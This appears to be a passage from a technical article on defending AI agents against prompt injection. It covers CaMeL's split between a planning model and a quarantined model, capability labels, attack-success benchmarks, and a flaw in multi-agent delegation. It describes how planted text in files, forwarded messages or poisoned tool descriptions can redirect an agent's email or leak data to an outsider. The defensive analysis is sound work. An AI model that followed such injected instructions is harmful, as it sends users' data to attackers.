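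Yan describes several systems that produce rules limiting an agent's actions. Progent generates rules for tools and their arguments, AgentBound gives each MCP server a list of permissions, and MiniScope derives a permission hierarchy from a service's OAuth settings. These rules are for developers, but Yan wanted ordinary users to write their own in terms of consequences, such as spending money or deleting something, with the choices "allow", "ask" and "never".

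Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which put off most decisions until the agent acted. They then approved two thirds of the excess actions they were asked about, so 133 of the 148 excess actions that went through in this group had a person's explicit approval. Yan added people to this group after random assignment had ended, and the difference between this group and the automated group was not statistically reliable after correction for multiple tests. Still, nothing in the results suggests that writing their own rules protected people better.

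Rules about consequences also require a way to identify the consequences of using each tool. Yan built a proxy that uses a language model to infer them from the tool's name, description and input schema. In a simulation where the user had banned a category of action, the proxy let through 14% of the tools in that category. Yan concludes that it isn't reliable enough to be a security boundary on its own. The tests used honest descriptions, but a hostile server's operator could write misleading ones.

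### Keeping untrusted text away from the plan

CaMeL, which researchers at Google DeepMind published in March 2025, separates the model that chooses the actions from text that might contain instructions, instead of trying to catch bad actions at the end. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that it builds on a design he proposed in 2023, which uses two language models. A privileged model receives the user's request and can use tools but never reads untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools.

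In CaMeL, the privileged model turns the request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. For Jane's request, it might write this:

```python
report = read_file("reports/june.csv")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarize this report", report)
send_email(to="sam@example.org", subject="June sales", body=summary)
```

It writes the program before the report is opened, and an interpreter then runs the program line by line. The second line passes the planted instruction to the quarantined model, which may well follow it but can only return text. The program has one call to `send_email`, with Sam's address already in it, and nothing in the report can add another call.

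The planted text can still alter the summary, so Sam might receive false figures. A more serious case arises if Jane asks the agent to mail the summary to the person named in the report. The program then has to take the address from untrusted text:

```python
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the contact's address", report)
send_email(to=address, subject="June sales", body=summary)
```

An attacker who can edit the report can now choose the recipient without adding a step to the program. Willison's original design had this weakness. CaMeL addresses it by having the interpreter attach labels, called capabilities, to every value. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes two kinds, one for where a value came from and one for who may read it. The labels for this program might be as follows.

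| Value | Where it came from | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| `report` | File store | Jane and Sam |
| `summary` | File store, through `report` | Jane and Sam |
| `address` | File store, through `report` | Jane and Sam |

Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a small Python function that can use the labels. For example, a policy might allow `send_email` only if the recipient is allowed to read the body. If the recipient is the attacker's address, taken from the report, the policy blocks the call or prompts Jane for approval. She should see fewer prompts than if she approved every call, because they appear only in doubtful cases.

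Someone has to write and maintain these policies, a burden the CaMeL paper acknowledges. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says anything that requires ordinary users to think about security policies makes him nervous. He still considered CaMeL the first credible defense against prompt injection that didn't simply add more AI.

### Measured results and costs

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues tested CaMeL on recent models in October. They adapted AgentDojo so that a coordinating agent passes work to several specialized agents, and ran 949 attack cases per model. The figures below are attack success rates.

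| Model | Without CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Modified CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Flash Lite's low rate probably reflects limited capability rather than resistance to attack, because it completed only about 28% of ordinary tasks and may have failed at the attacker's tasks too.

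On a separate set of 112 ordinary professional tasks, CaMeL lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Some of this drop comes from CaMeL's design. The privileged model has to write the program that handles a tool's output before receiving any of that output, so every tool needs an exact description of what it returns. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add these descriptions themselves. The interpreter also can't add steps that the model generates only after reading a file.

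For GPT-5.5, CaMeL reduced success on ordinary tasks and prevented no attacks that the model wasn't already resisting. This doesn't rule out using it, because the benchmark's attacks are fixed. Peters-Gill and colleagues point to large tests in which adaptive attackers got past every leading model. CaMeL's protection comes from the structure of the program, so it doesn't depend on whether the model has seen a similar attack. Whether that protection justifies a 13-point drop in task success depends on what the agent can access.

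All of these tests ran CaMeL without policies, so they measured its protection against added steps but not against a changed address or a leaked file. They also did not measure how many refused tasks and extra prompts the policies would cause.

### Plans that cross from one agent to another

The few successful attacks in the third column had one cause. Suppose the coordinating agent asks one agent for a list of job applicants and another to send a summary to Julie. Its program might contain this line:

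```python
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie: {summary}")
```

The coordinating agent's planner never received the summary. But the second agent treats the entire message as its user's request, so its privileged model receives the summary as trusted text. In an experiment with GPT-5.2, an instruction hidden in the applicant database reached that model this way and added a line to the second agent's program that mailed the data to an outsider, even though each agent had followed CaMeL's rules. Peters-Gill and colleagues also prove that, under mild assumptions, any such group of agents has this weakness if one of its tools can return untrusted data.

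Their modified version splits the message in two:

```python
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie",
    variables={"summary": summary},
)
```

The second agent's planner sees only `message`, but its program can use `summary` without showing the planner its contents. The interpreter rejects a `message` that includes any data from a tool. The change lowered scores on the professional tasks by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models. This approach works only if both agents run the same system and keep each other's labels, which is much easier within one company than along a delegation chain that crosses several.

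Other successors work on single agents. CaMeL evaluates its policies as the program reaches each tool call, so it may stop a task after some actions have already taken effect. CaMeLoT adds a static check of the program before it runs. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) discusses a related system, FIDES, which also tracks where data came from but deliberately doesn't track secrets that leak through the choice of what to do next. For instance, if a program sends one of two harmless messages depending on a confidential figure, the recipient learns something about the figure by seeing which message arrives.

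*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) identifies a gap in CaMeL, which trusts the first prompt. If Jane pastes a stranger's text into her request, the privileged model treats it as hers. Tool descriptions raise the same problem for agents that use MCP. Peters-Gill and colleagues count them as trusted information that may shape the plan, because a planner can't write calls to tools it knows nothing about. But on an unfamiliar tool server, an outsider wrote those descriptions, and a poisoned one would reach the privileged model, which CaMeL keeps away from untrusted text.
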